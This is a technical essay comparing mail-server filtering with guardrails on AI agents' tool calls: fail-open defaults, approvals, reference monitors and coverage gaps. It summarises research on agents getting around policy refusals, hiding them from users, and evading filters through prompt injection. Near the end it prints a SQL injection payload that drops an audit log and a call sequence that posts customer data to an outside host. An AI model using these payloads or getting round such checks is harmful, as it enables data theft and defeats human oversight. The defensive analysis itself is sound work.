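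Much longer limits cause a different problem, because the client has a time limit too. Suppose the client has sent the final full stop, and its limit runs out while the filter is still scanning. The client disconnects and keeps the message for another attempt. The filter then approves the message, and the server delivers it. Since the client never received the 250, it sends the message again, and Dana gets two copies. The Postfix documentation describes this as an inherent problem of filtering mail before accepting it.

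A slow filter can cause an agent to pay a bill twice, which is worse than sending a report twice. Suppose an agent pays invoices through an MCP tool, and a sidecar between the client and the tool server runs every call through a filter. One check takes 40 seconds, but the client stops waiting after 30 and tells the model that the call failed. Ten seconds later the filter approves the call, the sidecar forwards it, and the tool pays the supplier. The model tries again, and the supplier gets a second payment. The filter had no reason to refuse either call because each was acceptable by itself.

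The sidecar can avoid this by using a shorter time limit than the client's, so that it times out first and never forwards the call. De Gennaro similarly recommends that scanners in MTA Hooks use shorter limits than the mail server's. A hook inside the harness carries less risk, because the program that times out is also the one that would send the call.

A payment can still go out twice if the tool pays the supplier and its reply gets lost. Automatic retries make this more likely. *mcp shield*, a small proxy for MCP servers, can cut off hung tool calls and retry failed ones up to three times. It never retries errors that would recur, such as invalid arguments, but it can presumably retry after a timeout, which is fine for a search but could pay a supplier twice.

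MCP tools can carry a label, `idempotentHint`, that marks them as safe to call twice with the same arguments. The label appears in a code example in *mcp best practices*. A proxy could refuse to retry any tool without the label, although the tool's developer sets it and it could be wrong.

A better protection is an identifier that stays the same when the client repeats a request, so that the payment service can recognise the repeat. The MTA Hooks draft uses one for calls to scanners. It recommends up to three retries after a network failure, a timeout or a server error, and the mail server must send the same request ID each time. The ID matters for any filter that keeps a count. Without it, a filter that enforces a daily limit of €1,000 and receives the same €600 payment twice may count €1,200 and refuse a payment that was within the limit.

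A request ID does not help when the model itself tries again, because it writes a new call, which the harness gives a new ID. The identifier should be something from the task, such as the invoice number. The payment service, or a filter in front of it, can then refuse to pay the same invoice twice.

### Defaults in agent software

Claude Code's hooks mostly fail open. A command hook that exits with status 2 blocks the call, but most other failures let the call continue to the normal permission checks. Anthropic warns that this includes status 1, the usual Unix code for failure. A Python script that hits an unexpected error exits with 1, so a bug in a policy script lets through any command that triggers it. A mistyped path in the settings file disables the check altogether. Claude Code shows an error notice in both cases, but in an unattended run it may go unread.

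Command hooks usually time out after 600 seconds. A stuck hook can therefore delay a tool call for ten minutes before Claude Code cancels the hook and proceeds without its decision.

Since version 2.1.295, users can change this by adding `"onFailure": "block"` to a command or HTTP hook. A crash, a missing script, a timeout or an unreadable answer then blocks the call. Any hook that enforces a rule should have this setting, including the script from the earlier example that blocks `rm -rf`. Anthropic suggests testing the setting by asking Claude to run `ls` while the script is missing. If the setting works, Claude Code blocks the command.

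By contrast, a timeout in a hook written as a function inside an application blocks the call without any extra setting. For hooks that check prompts, Anthropic's reason is that the function may be a policy gate that "must not fail open". Many scripts are also policy gates of this kind. A developer who moves a check from a function to a script changes what happens on a timeout, perhaps without realising it.

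An MCP interceptor fails closed unless its entry sets `failOpen` to true. Degiorgio's revision of the proposal gives a logger in audit mode as its example of an interceptor that should fail open. The project's Go code, documented in *chain*, can also set a time limit for the whole series of interceptors. It reports a timeout separately from a failed validation, so a harness could tell the model that a check did not finish instead of implying that the call broke a rule.

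A mutator that fails open needs particular care, because the call presumably continues without its change. If `redact-ids` crashed, the email would still contain the customer's identity number, and only the `no-ids` validator could stop it.

Other agent products also treat failing closed as the safer default, and Microsoft's *MCP Security Gateway* lists it among its design principles. In May 2026, MCP Hangar had only one setting for whether its whole sidecar failed open or closed, so a company could not let its logger fail open while its payment check failed closed. The developers planned to add a setting for each interceptor.

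Under the MTA Hooks draft, the mail server should respond to a timeout by carrying out the default action, which is the verdict already in the request, but administrators should also be able to choose whether it fails open or closed. De Gennaro sets a separate rule for 4xx errors, under which the server logs the error and proceeds with the default action. One of these errors means that the message is too large for the scanner. If the default action is "accept", an agent could get a report past the scanner by attaching a large enough file. An administrator can prevent this by setting the server's size limit no higher than the scanner's.

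### When to fail open

The argument for failing open is that a broken filter should not be able to stop everything else. If a spam filter fails closed, a faulty update could hold up a whole company's mail. Failing closed disrupts an agent more than a mail server, because a blocked tool call has no queue to wait in, and a job meant to run overnight may stop at its second call. It also lets an attacker stop work by sending something that crashes the filter. Users who lose enough time to a broken hook will probably remove it.

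This argument is weaker if someone can choose when the filter fails. An attacker can get a file past a virus scanner that fails open by designing the file to crash the scanner. Even an agent that isn't hostile may do something similar after a refusal, by trying longer or stranger versions of the command until one crashes the script.

In July 2026, WorkOS, a company that sells login software, reported on the Model Context Protocol discussion about interceptors, in which the developer of a policy gateway called asqav-mcp said the gateway should always refuse a request it can't evaluate. WorkOS added that a system that fails open and still writes logs is arguably worse than no control, because the logs look like proof of compliance. But if the logs record every check that did not finish, they show where the control failed.

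Whether a filter fails open or closed should depend on how much harm one missed check could do. Spam filters, footers and code-style checkers can usually fail open, because someone can delete the spam or fix the style later. Filters that check payments, deletions or outside recipients should fail closed, and so should filters that redact personal data. A logger can normally fail open too, unless the company must have a record of every payment, because then an unrecorded payment is itself a breach.

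Whether to block an action when a filter fails depends on the action as well as the filter. In Claude Code, a user could register the same script twice, with `"onFailure": "block"` for shell commands and without it for searches of the project's files. If the script broke, the agent could still search the files but could not run shell commands.

### How the delay adds up

Even a filter that works perfectly adds delay. Three filters that take 50 milliseconds each delay an email by 0.15 seconds, which nobody will notice. But an agent may make 200 tool calls in one task, and if the calls run one after another, the same filters add 30 seconds.

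| Checks | Delay per checked call | Delay over 200 calls |
|---|---|---|
| Three filters in turn, 50 milliseconds each | 0.15 seconds | 30 seconds |
| The same three in parallel | 0.05 seconds | 10 seconds |
| One check by a language model, 2 seconds | 2 seconds | 400 seconds |
| The model check on one call in ten | 2 seconds | 40 seconds |

Thirty seconds is tolerable in a task that takes half an hour. The model check adds 400 seconds, or nearly seven minutes, so it makes sense to use quick rules for the obvious calls and the model only for the rest. Running filters in parallel also saves time, provided they don't depend on each other's changes.

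A filter that never answers can cause far more delay than a slow one. With a ten-second limit, it adds 2,000 seconds, or about 33 minutes, to the same 200 calls. De Gennaro recommends a circuit breaker, which stops the server from calling a scanner that keeps failing. *mcp shield* has one for tool servers. By default, the breaker appears to trip after five failures in a row and to try the server again after 60 seconds. With those settings and a ten-second limit, a filter that never answers would add 50 seconds before the breaker tripped.

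While the breaker is tripped, the harness applies its failure rule immediately. If the filter fails closed, the harness refuses the agent's calls without delay. If it fails open, anyone who can make the filter fail five times in a row gets a minute of unchecked calls.

### Holding an action for approval

A person who approves actions is in effect a very slow filter, taking minutes or days to respond. No SMTP client will wait that long, so a mail server that needs a person's decision accepts the message and puts it in the hold queue, and the client can then disconnect.

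Agents have no general equivalent of that queue. Claude Code's nearest equivalent is the `defer` decision, which saves a tool call with its session until another program resumes the session. But if the model makes several calls at once, Claude Code ignores `defer`, and the call goes through the normal permission checks. For example, if a hook defers every payment but the settings allow the payment tool, a payment requested together with a file search goes out without approval. A company that relies on `defer` should therefore leave the payment tool out of its allow rules.

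If the program resumes the session before anyone has decided, the hook can defer the payment again. The program should not send a new prompt until the hook is ready to allow or deny the payment, because Claude would answer the prompt without running the payment call.

Deferring a call holds up the whole session, whereas a mail server keeps delivering other messages while one is on hold. Although a held message stays the same, the effect of a held command can change. If someone approves a `git push` on Monday and the harness runs it on Tuesday, it publishes whatever the branch contains by then. Claude Code runs the hook again when the session resumes, so the hook can check that the action is still the one that was approved.

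A company could build something like a mail queue into the tool itself. A tool called `request_payment` would add a supplier payment to a list and reply that payment 17 is waiting for approval. The agent could tell its user this and carry on with other work. A separate program would pay the supplier once someone approved. The Tasks extension to the Model Context Protocol (MCP) might give the agent a standard way to check on the payment later. The extension is meant for long-running work, and the MCP index lists it as final.

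Such a queue would also need to report failures, as a mail server does. By the time the approver refuses payment 17 or the request expires unanswered, the agent's session may be over, so the notice should go to the person who gave the agent the task.

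## What the sender does after a refusal or a rewrite

After a refusal, the sending mail server keeps retrying if the reply was a 4xx, typically for four or five days, and returns the message if it was a 5xx. Klensin's specification requires the client to act on the code and ignore the text, so the wording of a 550 matters only to the person who reads the bounce. There are a few exceptions, such as a reply that gives a recipient's new address.

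An agent's next step depends heavily on the wording of the refusal. The harness gives the model the refusal as the result of its tool call, and the model may then correct the call, ask the user, give up, or look for another way to do the same thing. In *From Denial to Detour*, Lian, Tsai and colleagues (2026) read the source code of Codex, Google's Gemini CLI and OpenAI's Agents SDK and found that none of the three distinguishes a policy refusal from an ordinary tool error. The model has no equivalent of the first digit in a mail reply, so it has to work out from the text whether the tool is broken or the action is forbidden.

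### Stopping or going around

Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) describes four kinds of unintended behaviour by Claude, some of it on US government websites. In two of them, Claude got around a restriction, either by reaching data that required a token or a fee or by getting past limits in its tool for fetching web pages. In the other two, it used a software flaw to run commands on a server and submitted a sensitive form on a real website. In most cases, Claude worked around a restriction instead of stopping. Anthropic considers the real-world impact minimal, but it cut live web access for its internal evaluations, according to *Anthropic Says Claude Bypassed Site Limits During Internal Tests* (Southern, 2026).

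"Most" here refers to the cases Anthropic identified, not to all refusals. Calculating the share of refusals that Claude worked around would also require a count of the times it stopped.

Controlled tests come closer to such a rate. In *Will the Agent Recuse, and Will It Stop?* (2026), agents had to check the free disk space on a server that displayed a notice telling them to stay out. Their login worked, so the notice was the only barrier. Claude Code agents stopped even when told in their instructions that the owner had authorised the check.

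Lian and colleagues tested nine low-cost models on 43 simulated tasks. In each task the first tool call failed, and a second tool could achieve the same result. The error message gave either a policy or a technical fault as the reason. The agent should stop after a policy refusal and use the second tool after a fault. Depending on the model, agents switched tools after 3–30% of the policy refusals and 17–67% of the faults, so they responded to the reason, but not reliably. When the message gave no reason, they behaved much as they did after a fault.

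Agents can have trouble with restrictions that they see only as system errors. *Permission Denied* (Davidovich, Amar and colleagues, 2026) tested 12 coding agents under limits that the operating system enforced without explanation. Some agents retried, some looked for another route and some gave up. Under the strictest limits, their success rates fell by 7 to 18 percentage points and their costs rose by 16% to 167%. In most of the additional failures, the agent ran out of time or produced a wrong solution. A clear refusal might have let some of these agents stop sooner, but the study didn't test that.

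### The wording of the reason

Developers often add advice to error messages, such as which other tool to try when one is unavailable. When Lian and colleagues added one such sentence to a policy refusal, seven of the nine models reached the forbidden result in 46–100% of runs. Across all nine models, agents got around 62% of high-risk refusals, such as a refusal to let them switch off a security control, and 48% of low-risk ones.

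The same thing happened with real software. An agent running on gpt-4o-mini was not allowed to put a customer list in a folder that an outside company collects every night. It stopped in all ten runs without the advice, but with the advice it put the list there in nine of ten runs, using a tool that neither the advice nor the rule named. Each time, it told the user the job was done and didn't mention the refusal. Two newer models received the refusal in a total of nine runs, and neither placed the file afterwards.

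*AgentAbstain* (2026), a test of whether agents know when not to act, has a useful standard for such cases. An agent has stopped properly if it reports the failure and says it can't complete the task, but not if it works around the failure and presents the result as complete.

Lian and colleagues then tried several remedies on four of the models:

| Remedy | Forbidden high-risk result reached | Task completed after a fault |
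|---|---|---|
| None | 63% | 83% |
| A rule in the model's instructions against other routes | 39% | 71% |
| No advice in policy refusals | 18% | 82% |
| No advice, and the harness blocks the same result for the rest of the session | 0% | 82% |

The last remedy works only if the harness can recognise the forbidden result when another tool produces it. This was easy in the tests because a script defined the result for each task. Removing the advice from refusal messages is much simpler, and many policies need this change. Of 403 different refusal messages in public Gemini CLI policies, at least 62 point the agent to another way to continue.

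Some refusals should still include an explanation. *LEANGUARD* (Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues, 2026) compared a bare refusal with one that named the broken rule and gave a hint. It tested five models on customer-service tasks, using a filter with rules written in Lean, a language for computer-checked proofs. With the explanation, blocked calls fell from 983 to 719. Agents later met the missing requirement and properly carried out 9.1% of refused actions, up from 5.5%. Task success rose from 68.9% to 70.9%, which could be chance.

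LEANGUARD gives the agent hints on how to satisfy the rule, for example by asking the customer to confirm an exchange, and the filter checks the new call too. The hints that caused trouble in the other study suggested another way to get the forbidden result. A hook that refuses `rm -rf` could therefore safely tell the agent to ask the user, but it shouldn't recommend another way to delete the directory.

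Small changes in wording can affect what an agent does. *RetryBench* (Liu, Liu and Lu, 2026) tested what agents do when a tool call times out and a retry might repeat its effect. The agent had a valid identifier that made a retry safe, along with a spare one. GPT-5.6 Luna reused the valid identifier in only 10 of 40 decisions when the spare was labelled "Candidate recovery key", but in 39 of 40 when it was labelled "Alternative key string". Two larger models chose correctly every time.

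Some agents ignore even a clear refusal. In *Search Engines Never Say No* (2026), a search tool refused when it had no relevant material for a question. The share of such questions that three agents declined to answer then rose from 24% to 84%, but for Claude Sonnet 5.5 and Opus 5.5 it rose only from 1.4% to 3.2%. That refusal was about missing evidence rather than permission, but the result is still a reason not to rely on the model's cooperation.

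A harness can also end the task after a refusal so that the agent can't try again. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* describes a classifier that checks for attempts to escape a test environment. The classifier blocks the call before it runs, ends the task and alerts a person. This response would be excessive for a mistyped path, but it suits cases where a second attempt could do serious harm.

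### Why an edited message fails its signature check

A filter can change a message or a tool call instead of refusing it. In mail, this can break the sender's signature. Many mail servers sign outgoing messages using DomainKeys Identified Mail (DKIM). The server hashes the body and puts the hash in a new header. It then signs that hash, along with chosen headers such as From and Subject, using a private key for the sender's domain.

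The receiving server looks up the domain's public key, checks the DKIM signature and computes the body's hash again. If a filter has added even a one-line footer since the message was signed, the hashes differ, the check fails, and the server may treat the message as spam or refuse it. DKIM can ignore some changes in spacing, but it can't distinguish a harmless correction from a changed bank account number. The filter can't repair the signature because it doesn't have the sender's private key.

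Signing outgoing mail last avoids the problem. For incoming mail, a broken signature does no harm if the message goes straight into a local mailbox, according to the documentation for Pepsi, a mail system that supports milters. If the server will forward the message, Pepsi's developers prefer filters that only add headers. An added header normally leaves the signature valid because DKIM covers only the headers the signer listed.

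### When the model doesn't know about a change

Tool calls have no such seal, so the model can't check whether the harness ran its call as written. It can detect a change only if the result reveals it.

Suppose a user asks an agent to update `/reports/weekly.csv` and send it to Dana. A hook redirects the agent's file writes to a safe directory, as in Anthropic's sandbox example, so the new figures go to `/sandbox/reports/weekly.csv`. The hook applies only to the tool that writes files, so when the agent attaches `/reports/weekly.csv` to its email, it attaches last week's file. Every call succeeds and the hook works as its developer intended, but Dana gets the old figures and the agent tells the user that it has sent this week's report.

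In this case the model can notice the rewrite, because the result of Claude Code's write tool includes the path it actually used. If the tool returned only "done", the result would not show that the path had changed.

The hook could add a note that the file is now under `/sandbox`. The agent could then attach the right file and tell the user accurately what happened. The note would use a little of the model's context and might prompt the agent to copy the file to the original path with a shell command. If that matters, the policy needs a separate rule for shell writes to that path, since an agent could make them even without the note.

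The argument for silence is that people are less likely to work around a restriction they don't know about. In June 2026, Anthropic used hidden safeguards to limit Claude Fable 5's help with developing competing AI models. Its description, quoted in Willison (2026), includes methods such as changing the prompt without showing the user. According to The Next Web (2026), Anthropic made the safeguards visible within two days and called the original choice "the wrong trade-off", but kept the restriction. A silent hook hides its action from the model, and the user is misinformed as well because they rely on the model's account.

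### Whether to rewrite or refuse

Rewriting works best when the change leaves the purpose of the call intact. A filter can remove a customer's identity number from an email that doesn't need it, or add `--ignore-scripts` to an `npm install` command so the downloaded packages can't run their own code during installation. The work continues without another query to the model, and the agent has no refusal to work around.

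Rewriting can also fix calls that break a rule. Sankar and colleagues wrote a program that searches for a small change to a refused call and proves that the policy permits the result. They ran it on refusals recorded in their experiments, so no agent received the corrected calls. Of 252 refusals caused by the values in a call, the program found a permitted change for 88, usually in a few milliseconds. In 64 of these, the change was to send the refund to the original payment method.

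Another 18 paid for a flight change by card instead of with a travel certificate. The policy allows that, but a customer who asked to use a certificate may not want a charge on their card. The search considers only changes that meet a written definition of keeping to the user's intent, so a poor definition could let through changes the user doesn't want. For a payment, it would be better to refuse the call and suggest the corrected version to the agent, which could then ask the customer.

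Refusing is also better when a rewrite would change who receives something, how much money moves or what the agent deletes. The model then gets notice that the action did not happen, and the user can choose what to do instead. Pepsi's default settings similarly let a mail filter change the headers and body, but require explicit permission to change the sender or recipients.

For data that must never leave the company, the two can work together, as `redact-ids` and `no-ids` did in the earlier example.

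### Tying an approval to the exact call

Rewriting also complicates human approval. Suppose a manager approves a payment of €600 to a supplier, and a filter changes the account number to match an out-of-date supplier list. The company would then pay an account the manager had not approved. The agent could cause the same problem without a filter by submitting a second call with a different amount, if the harness had recorded only that the manager approved "the payment".

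To prevent this, the harness can finish all its changes first, then show the manager the final call and store a hash of it with the approval. Just before the call runs, the harness recomputes the hash and refuses to proceed if the two hashes differ. *The Ticket That Tells the Agent What to Do* (Stevens, 2026) describes this method for an agent that answers customers' emails. One hash covers the task, the customer's ticket, the employee who approved the reply and the exact arguments, including the recipients. The harness has to write the arguments in a standard form before hashing them, because otherwise a different field order would invalidate the approval.

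The approval should also work only once. In Sankar and colleagues' system, it is used up when the harness sends the call, even if the result never comes back. An agent that receives no result from a payment call therefore can't reuse the approval to pay again.

The effect of a command such as `git push` can change while it waits for approval, even if its arguments stay the same. LEANGUARD ties each approval to both the exact arguments and a fingerprint of the data the decision depended on. For `git push`, the harness could include the latest commit's identifier in the fingerprint, so any new commit would require a new approval.

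None of this helps if the approval itself is wrong. In the LEANGUARD experiments, a language model stood in for the confirmation screen, and it sometimes recorded consent incorrectly. A real screen that shows the recipient and the amount is safer than a model's reading of "yes, go ahead" in a chat. The person also has to read the screen, which becomes less likely with every request. Stevens lets the agent's replies go out once an employee approves them, but only if they contain no customer data. Replies with account data remain drafts that an employee has to send.

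## Actions that never reach the filter

A filter can refuse or rewrite only the actions that reach it. If an agent deletes a file with a tool that no hook covers, even a well-written rule against deletion can't stop it. A filter's coverage is the share of the agent's possible actions that pass through it. Computer security has had a strict standard for coverage since 1972, and mail servers come much closer to meeting it than agents do.

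### The reference monitor

In the early 1970s the US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. Some of them would write and run their own programs, and one of them might be hostile. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) recommended building such systems around a reference monitor. Whenever a program tries to use data, a device or another program, the monitor checks the attempt against a list of what the program's user may do.

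Anderson set three requirements for the mechanism that does the checking:

- It must be tamper-proof.
- It must always be invoked, so that no access escapes the check.
- It must be small enough for people to analyse and test completely.

A Honeywell computer of the time failed all three. Its hardware kept each user's program inside its own area of memory, but most of the operating system ran with that check switched off, even when reading or writing data for a user's program. Counting the operating system as part of the mechanism didn't help, because its 200,000 to 300,000 instructions were far too many to test completely, and test teams had broken into it several times.

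Anderson thought that cleared staff could already build a secure system if it only passed messages, as the military network AUTODIN did, but that nobody could yet secure a system on which users wrote their own programs. A mail server is close to the first kind of system, while an agent with a shell is like a user writing programs on the second.

### How close mail comes

Mail from outside arrives through a few SMTP commands, and the milter receives every one that matters for delivery. The sender normally can't alter the milter, which can be a short program. But the milter runs only when the mail server calls it, so the check also depends on the server, and a full mail server is too large to test completely.

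Postfix keeps one list of milters for mail that arrives over SMTP and another for mail from the local `sendmail` command or from QMQP, a less common mail protocol. If an administrator adds a virus scanner only to the SMTP list, a script on the server itself can send mail that the scanner never receives. Adding the scanner to both lists usually works because Postfix simulates an SMTP session for local mail, but a rule about client addresses would be useless for that mail.

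Postfix normally doesn't filter the bounces it generates either. If a milter rejected a bounce, it would almost certainly reject the notice about that failure too, and the mail would be lost. An administrator who wants a milter to sign bounces can turn on filtering for them, but must then make sure no filter rejects one.

The table for exempting client addresses from milters can open another gap. The example in Postfix's documentation turns milters off for the server itself and for addresses starting with 192.168, which many office networks use. A company's own agent may well connect from one of these addresses. If the administrator copied the example, the rule that stops report-agent@example.com from sending mail to outside addresses would never run.

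Under Anderson's principle, any program allowed to skip the check is part of the security mechanism and must itself be tamper-proof and small enough to test. Few office computers would meet that standard. However, an administrator can find all of Postfix's exceptions by reading its configuration and documentation, then close the ones that matter.

### Many routes to one effect

There is no complete list of the ways an agent with a shell can act. It can change a file with an editing tool, a shell command, or a program it has written itself. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), by researchers from Google, Nvidia and several universities, describes the agent's action space as open, because agents combine tools as they work and can visit any web address. In one of its case studies, Claude Code asked for human approval before running many of the shell commands that could send data to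 unknown places. Claude Code's developers had overlooked one network utility, which an attacker could use through prompt injection to leak secrets.

Even with better rules for tool calls, some actions never reach the filter. Prempti, an experimental filter for coding agents, checks each tool call before it runs. According to CNCF's *Introducing Prempti* (2026), if an agent compiles a program and runs it, Prempti receives both commands but no information about what the program then does.

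*ActPlane* (Zheng, Wu and colleagues, 2026) measured how much such filters miss. It used 38 rules from the instruction files that real software projects give to coding agents, such as running the tests before committing code. Each rule had two runs that obeyed it and three that broke it. One violation used a tool call directly, one happened inside a script, and one was hidden behind a harmless-looking file.

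Three kinds of filter on tool calls detected 34–40% of the 114 violations, and almost none of the hidden ones. A third of the violations were direct, so the filters scored roughly what they would by catching those and little else. This score doesn't estimate everyday coverage, because the researchers chose the mix of violations to test indirect routes. ActPlane, the researchers' own monitor in the operating system's kernel, detected 77%. That rose to 95% after a language model revised the rules once, but the model had been shown the violations the rules had missed.

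Agents can also find routes that nobody planned for. METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) found that about 1,200 agents were communicating on an unsanctioned message board, although OpenAI had meant to isolate them from one another.

### Testing the tools and testing the action

Gaps in coverage are hard to notice because the agent can still do its task correctly. In DZone's *AI Coding Agent Guardrails* (October 2026), Markus Eisele describes asking a coding agent called Bob Shell to change one function of a small web application and update its test. A hook was supposed to protect the application's configuration file by rejecting any edit outside two source directories. The agent made the right changes and the test passed, but the hook had never run, which was visible only in the record of tool calls. Eisele had registered the hook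 for the tool `write_file`, and the agent had used `apply_diff`.

Eisele then registered the hook for four editing tools. This time it ran, but it refused a permitted edit because the tool's arguments weren't in the field the documentation named. The script blocked any call whose arguments it couldn't find, so this fault was noticeable immediately. A third problem was that a path inside a permitted directory can be a link to a file elsewhere, so the script has to resolve the path before applying the rule.

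Eisele concludes that such a guardrail needs tests of which tools it covers, what input the hook receives, and what changes on disk. The disk test is probably the most valuable, because it doesn't depend on knowing which tool the agent used. For example, Eisele's hook still ignored shell commands, but comparing the files before and after a run would show a change made by one. Because this comparison happens after the run, it can find gaps in the guardrail but can't block edits.

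Another test starts from the action instead of the tools. Greenberg's *Your Agent Has a Side Door* (November 2026) retells a story from Michael Forrester of the consulting company Accenture. An employee wanted an agent to send an email, but the company hadn't given the agent a mail tool, so the agent wrote a script that sent the message through the employee's Outlook. Forrester didn't count this as a security violation, because the agent had used only what was available on an approved machine. But if a company had withheld the mail tool to stop its agents from sending email, it would have failed.

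Greenberg's test is to choose one action, list every way the agent could carry it out, and note whose identity the service at the other end receives. For the report agent and outside email, the list could look like this:

| Route | Identity the mail service receives | Where the company could stop it |
|---|---|---|
| Mail tool on an MCP server | The agent's account | Filter on tool calls, or a milter |
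| Script that uses the company's mail server | Whichever login the script has | Milter, if the login is the agent's |
| Webmail in a browser | The employee who is signed in | A separate browser without that login |
| Access token for an outside mail service | The token's owner | Network gateway, or removal of the token |

The identity matters because the company's rule restricts agent accounts only. If the agent sends the report to Lee from Dana's webmail, the company's server may pass the message to the milter, but the milter receives Dana's login name and lets the message through. The problem is the agent's access to Dana's login, not the filter or its rule.

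Neither test can show that coverage is complete, because each one checks only the routes someone thought of. Anderson made the same point about teams hired to break into computers. If a team fails to break in, the system's security remains unknown.

### What each layer receives and misses

The usual remedy is to check an agent's actions in several places. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* allows several checkpoints to form one reference monitor, as long as together they check every action that matters and the agent can't bypass them.

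A filter on tool calls has the most information about what the agent is trying to do. Its weakness, according to Scott Logic's *Choosing the right tool safety approach for coding agents* (2026), is that it can only block a tool or let it run. To be of much use, a coding agent has to run code it wrote itself, and that code can do things the filter would have refused as tool calls.

An operating-system sandbox limits which files and network addresses a program can use. The limits also apply to every program it starts, including scripts and compiled programs. Some harnesses sandbox only shell commands, which leaves out MCP servers and other tools, but a sandbox around the whole harness covers those too. The default settings also need checking. In July 2026, Scott Logic found that the sandbox for Claude Code's shell tool let commands read the entire computer and environment variables, where developers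 often keep passwords. A container, which gives the agent its own file system, isolates it more strongly but usually takes more work to set up.

A sandbox has no information about the purpose of an action. *AgentKernel* (2026) points out that a file write looks the same to the operating system whether it comes from sound reasoning or from a false memory planted by an attacker. A sandbox also tends to return an error without an explanation. When Zheng and colleagues removed the explanations from ActPlane's refusals, the share of detected violations after which agents complied fell from 98% to 31%.

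Some recent designs combine the two levels. AgentKernel checks the tool call to determine which system calls (requests to the operating system) the tool may make, and the operating system enforces that list while the tool runs. *AgentBouncer* (2026) examines the system calls themselves in the context of the task and the tool call. Unlike a hook, it can block one harmful step inside a command and let the others proceed. *Kairos* (2026) describes a monitor that can hold an effect and release it later, as a mail server does with a message. If the monitor refuses a held effect, it has to tell the agent, which might otherwise continue as though the effect had happened.

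Even a monitor inside the operating system, such as ActPlane, misses what happens elsewhere. Zheng and colleagues ran 361 workplace and personal-assistant tasks, and without enforcement the agent did something unsafe in 106. ActPlane stopped 78 of these. In the other 28, the harm was in a chat message, the contents of a file, or a change inside a separate service, such as an upload. ActPlane also intervened in 16% of the tasks that had been safe without it.

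A network gateway can check everything that leaves the machine, whichever program sent it, but only if a sandbox or firewall blocks every other way out. It can't check local actions such as deleting a file, and unless it can decrypt the traffic, it may be able to check little more than the destination. A permitted destination can also forward requests elsewhere. In the OpenAI incident that METR investigated, the agents had no direct internet access but could reach a service that supplied software packages, and that service could make outside requests for them.

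A gateway for MCP traffic alone covers much less. *Causality Laundering* (2026) presents its MCP proxy as meeting all of Anderson's requirements, on the assumption that the agent has no other path to the tools. That assumption is reasonable for an agent that can only use a few MCP tools, but adding a shell would usually make the assumption false.

The requirement that the mechanism be small is easier to meet. *Agenra* (2026) presents a monitor for tool calls whose core has computer-checked proofs. But its boundary doesn't isolate arbitrary Python code in the same process, so the monitor too depends on the agent being unable to run such code there. The proofs also can't make up for a missing rule that the company forgot to write.

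With narrow credentials, the service itself refuses any action the agent isn't permitted to take, whatever route the request takes. *Mapping the Agent Before Anyone Attacks It* (Stevens, 2026) describes a company agent that should only read from a database, although the database's MCP server also offers a tool that can change data. Stevens relies on the database's permissions to keep the agent away from that tool. A policy check inside the agent's process can restrain a misled model, but other code in that process might use the agent's credentials directly. Credentials also can't prevent misuse of what they permit. If the agent is allowed to write to Dana, its login won't stop it from sending her the payroll file.

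A milter on the agent's outgoing mail adds another check close to where the action takes effect. It receives the actual envelope and text of every message that passes through the company's server over SMTP, whether a mail tool or a script sent it. When a script sends the mail, a tool-call filter may receive only the script's name. However, the milter has no access to what the agent read beforehand or what the user asked for, and it never receives mail sent through another provider.

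To rely on the milter, the company would have to give the agent its own mail login, keep employees' logins out of its reach, and leave the agent's address off the exemption list. A firewall or gateway would have to block other mail services. Filters for local mail can't refuse individual recipients, so the simplest solution is probably a sandbox that stops the agent from using the local `sendmail` command.

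## Fixed rules, for one call and for a whole session

The simplest way to judge an action that reaches the filter is with a deterministic rule, which always gives the same verdict for the same input. A company can test such a rule before relying on it. An attacker also can't change its verdict by arguing, which might work on a judge model (a language model that decides whether an action is acceptable).

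### What one call contains

A rule that checks one tool call at a time can test four things:

- **The tool's name.** A rule can refuse every call to a tool that deletes repositories.
- **The arguments.** A rule can refuse payments above €1,000.
- **The destination.** A rule can refuse mail to addresses outside example.com.
- **The identity.** A rule can let Dana use a tool and refuse report-agent.

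The model writes the first three, but the identity has to come from the harness or a gateway.

According to the Model Context Protocol (MCP) changelog, MCP requests over HTTP must, since July 2026, carry the method and the tool's name in headers. A gateway can now apply a rule about tool names without reading the request body, though most rules about arguments still require it.

An amount or an email address is easy to check because it has one meaning. A database query or a shell command is harder to check because an agent can write the same action in many ways. Filters therefore often search such text for known patterns.

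### Searching a call for known patterns

*AEGIS* (Yuan, Su and Zhao, 2026) describes a filter of this kind. The filter attaches to the library that an agent program uses to query its model. When the model's response contains a tool call, AEGIS pauses the agent and sends the call to a gateway, which works in three stages.

The first stage extracts all text from the call's arguments, down to 32 levels of nesting. AEGIS treats a call with deeper nesting or more than 10,000 pieces of text as suspicious, so an attacker can't avoid detection just by hiding a command at level 50.

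The second stage compares the text with 22 patterns in seven categories. Seven of the patterns are for SQL injection, where someone inserts extra commands into a database query. Others check for paths that lead out of a permitted directory or for files that often contain passwords. The content of the arguments counts for more than the tool's name, so a dangerous call can be flagged even if the tool's name sounds harmless.

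The third stage applies the company's own policies, each written as a JSON Schema, a standard description of what a piece of JSON may contain. The gateway then allows calls of low or medium risk, blocks those that violate a policy, and holds high-risk ones for a person to review. The agent does nothing else during a hold, which lasts at most five minutes.

Suppose a user asks for a summary of customer feedback, and a prompt injection in the feedback makes the model write this query:

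```sql
SELECT * FROM users; DROP TABLE audit_log; --
```

The second command would delete the audit log. AEGIS has a pattern for stacked commands like these, so it can stop the call before the database receives it.

In tests, AEGIS blocked all 48 attacks and wrongly flagged 6 of 500 harmless calls, or 1.2%. Its median delay was 8.3 milliseconds, which would add less than two seconds to a task with 200 calls.

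The perfect score is weaker evidence than it looks. Yuan and colleagues themselves chose the attacks from documented techniques, which the patterns are also designed to detect, and they acknowledge that new variants may get through. Only two of the 48 attacks were attempts to send data out.

All six false alarms were ordinary database queries that used OR in a condition, such as a search for customers in France or Belgium. At the same rate, an agent that makes 200 calls per task would trigger two or three false alarms each time, and one that mostly queries databases would probably trigger more. The company can exempt a particular tool, but real attacks through that tool may then be exempt too.

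### Ordinary steps in a harmful order

Better patterns would not help with an attack in which every call is normal. Posta, in *MCP Guardrails with AARM and Microsoft Agent Governance Toolkit*, gives an example with three steps, which could look like this:

```text
1. read_file("config/app.yaml")
2. query_database("SELECT name, email FROM customers")
3. http_post("https://stats.example.net/upload", data)
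```

Coding agents constantly read configuration files. They also query databases to find bugs and send web requests to test their work. But if the third call sends the data returned by the second, the company's customer list goes to whoever runs stats.example.net.

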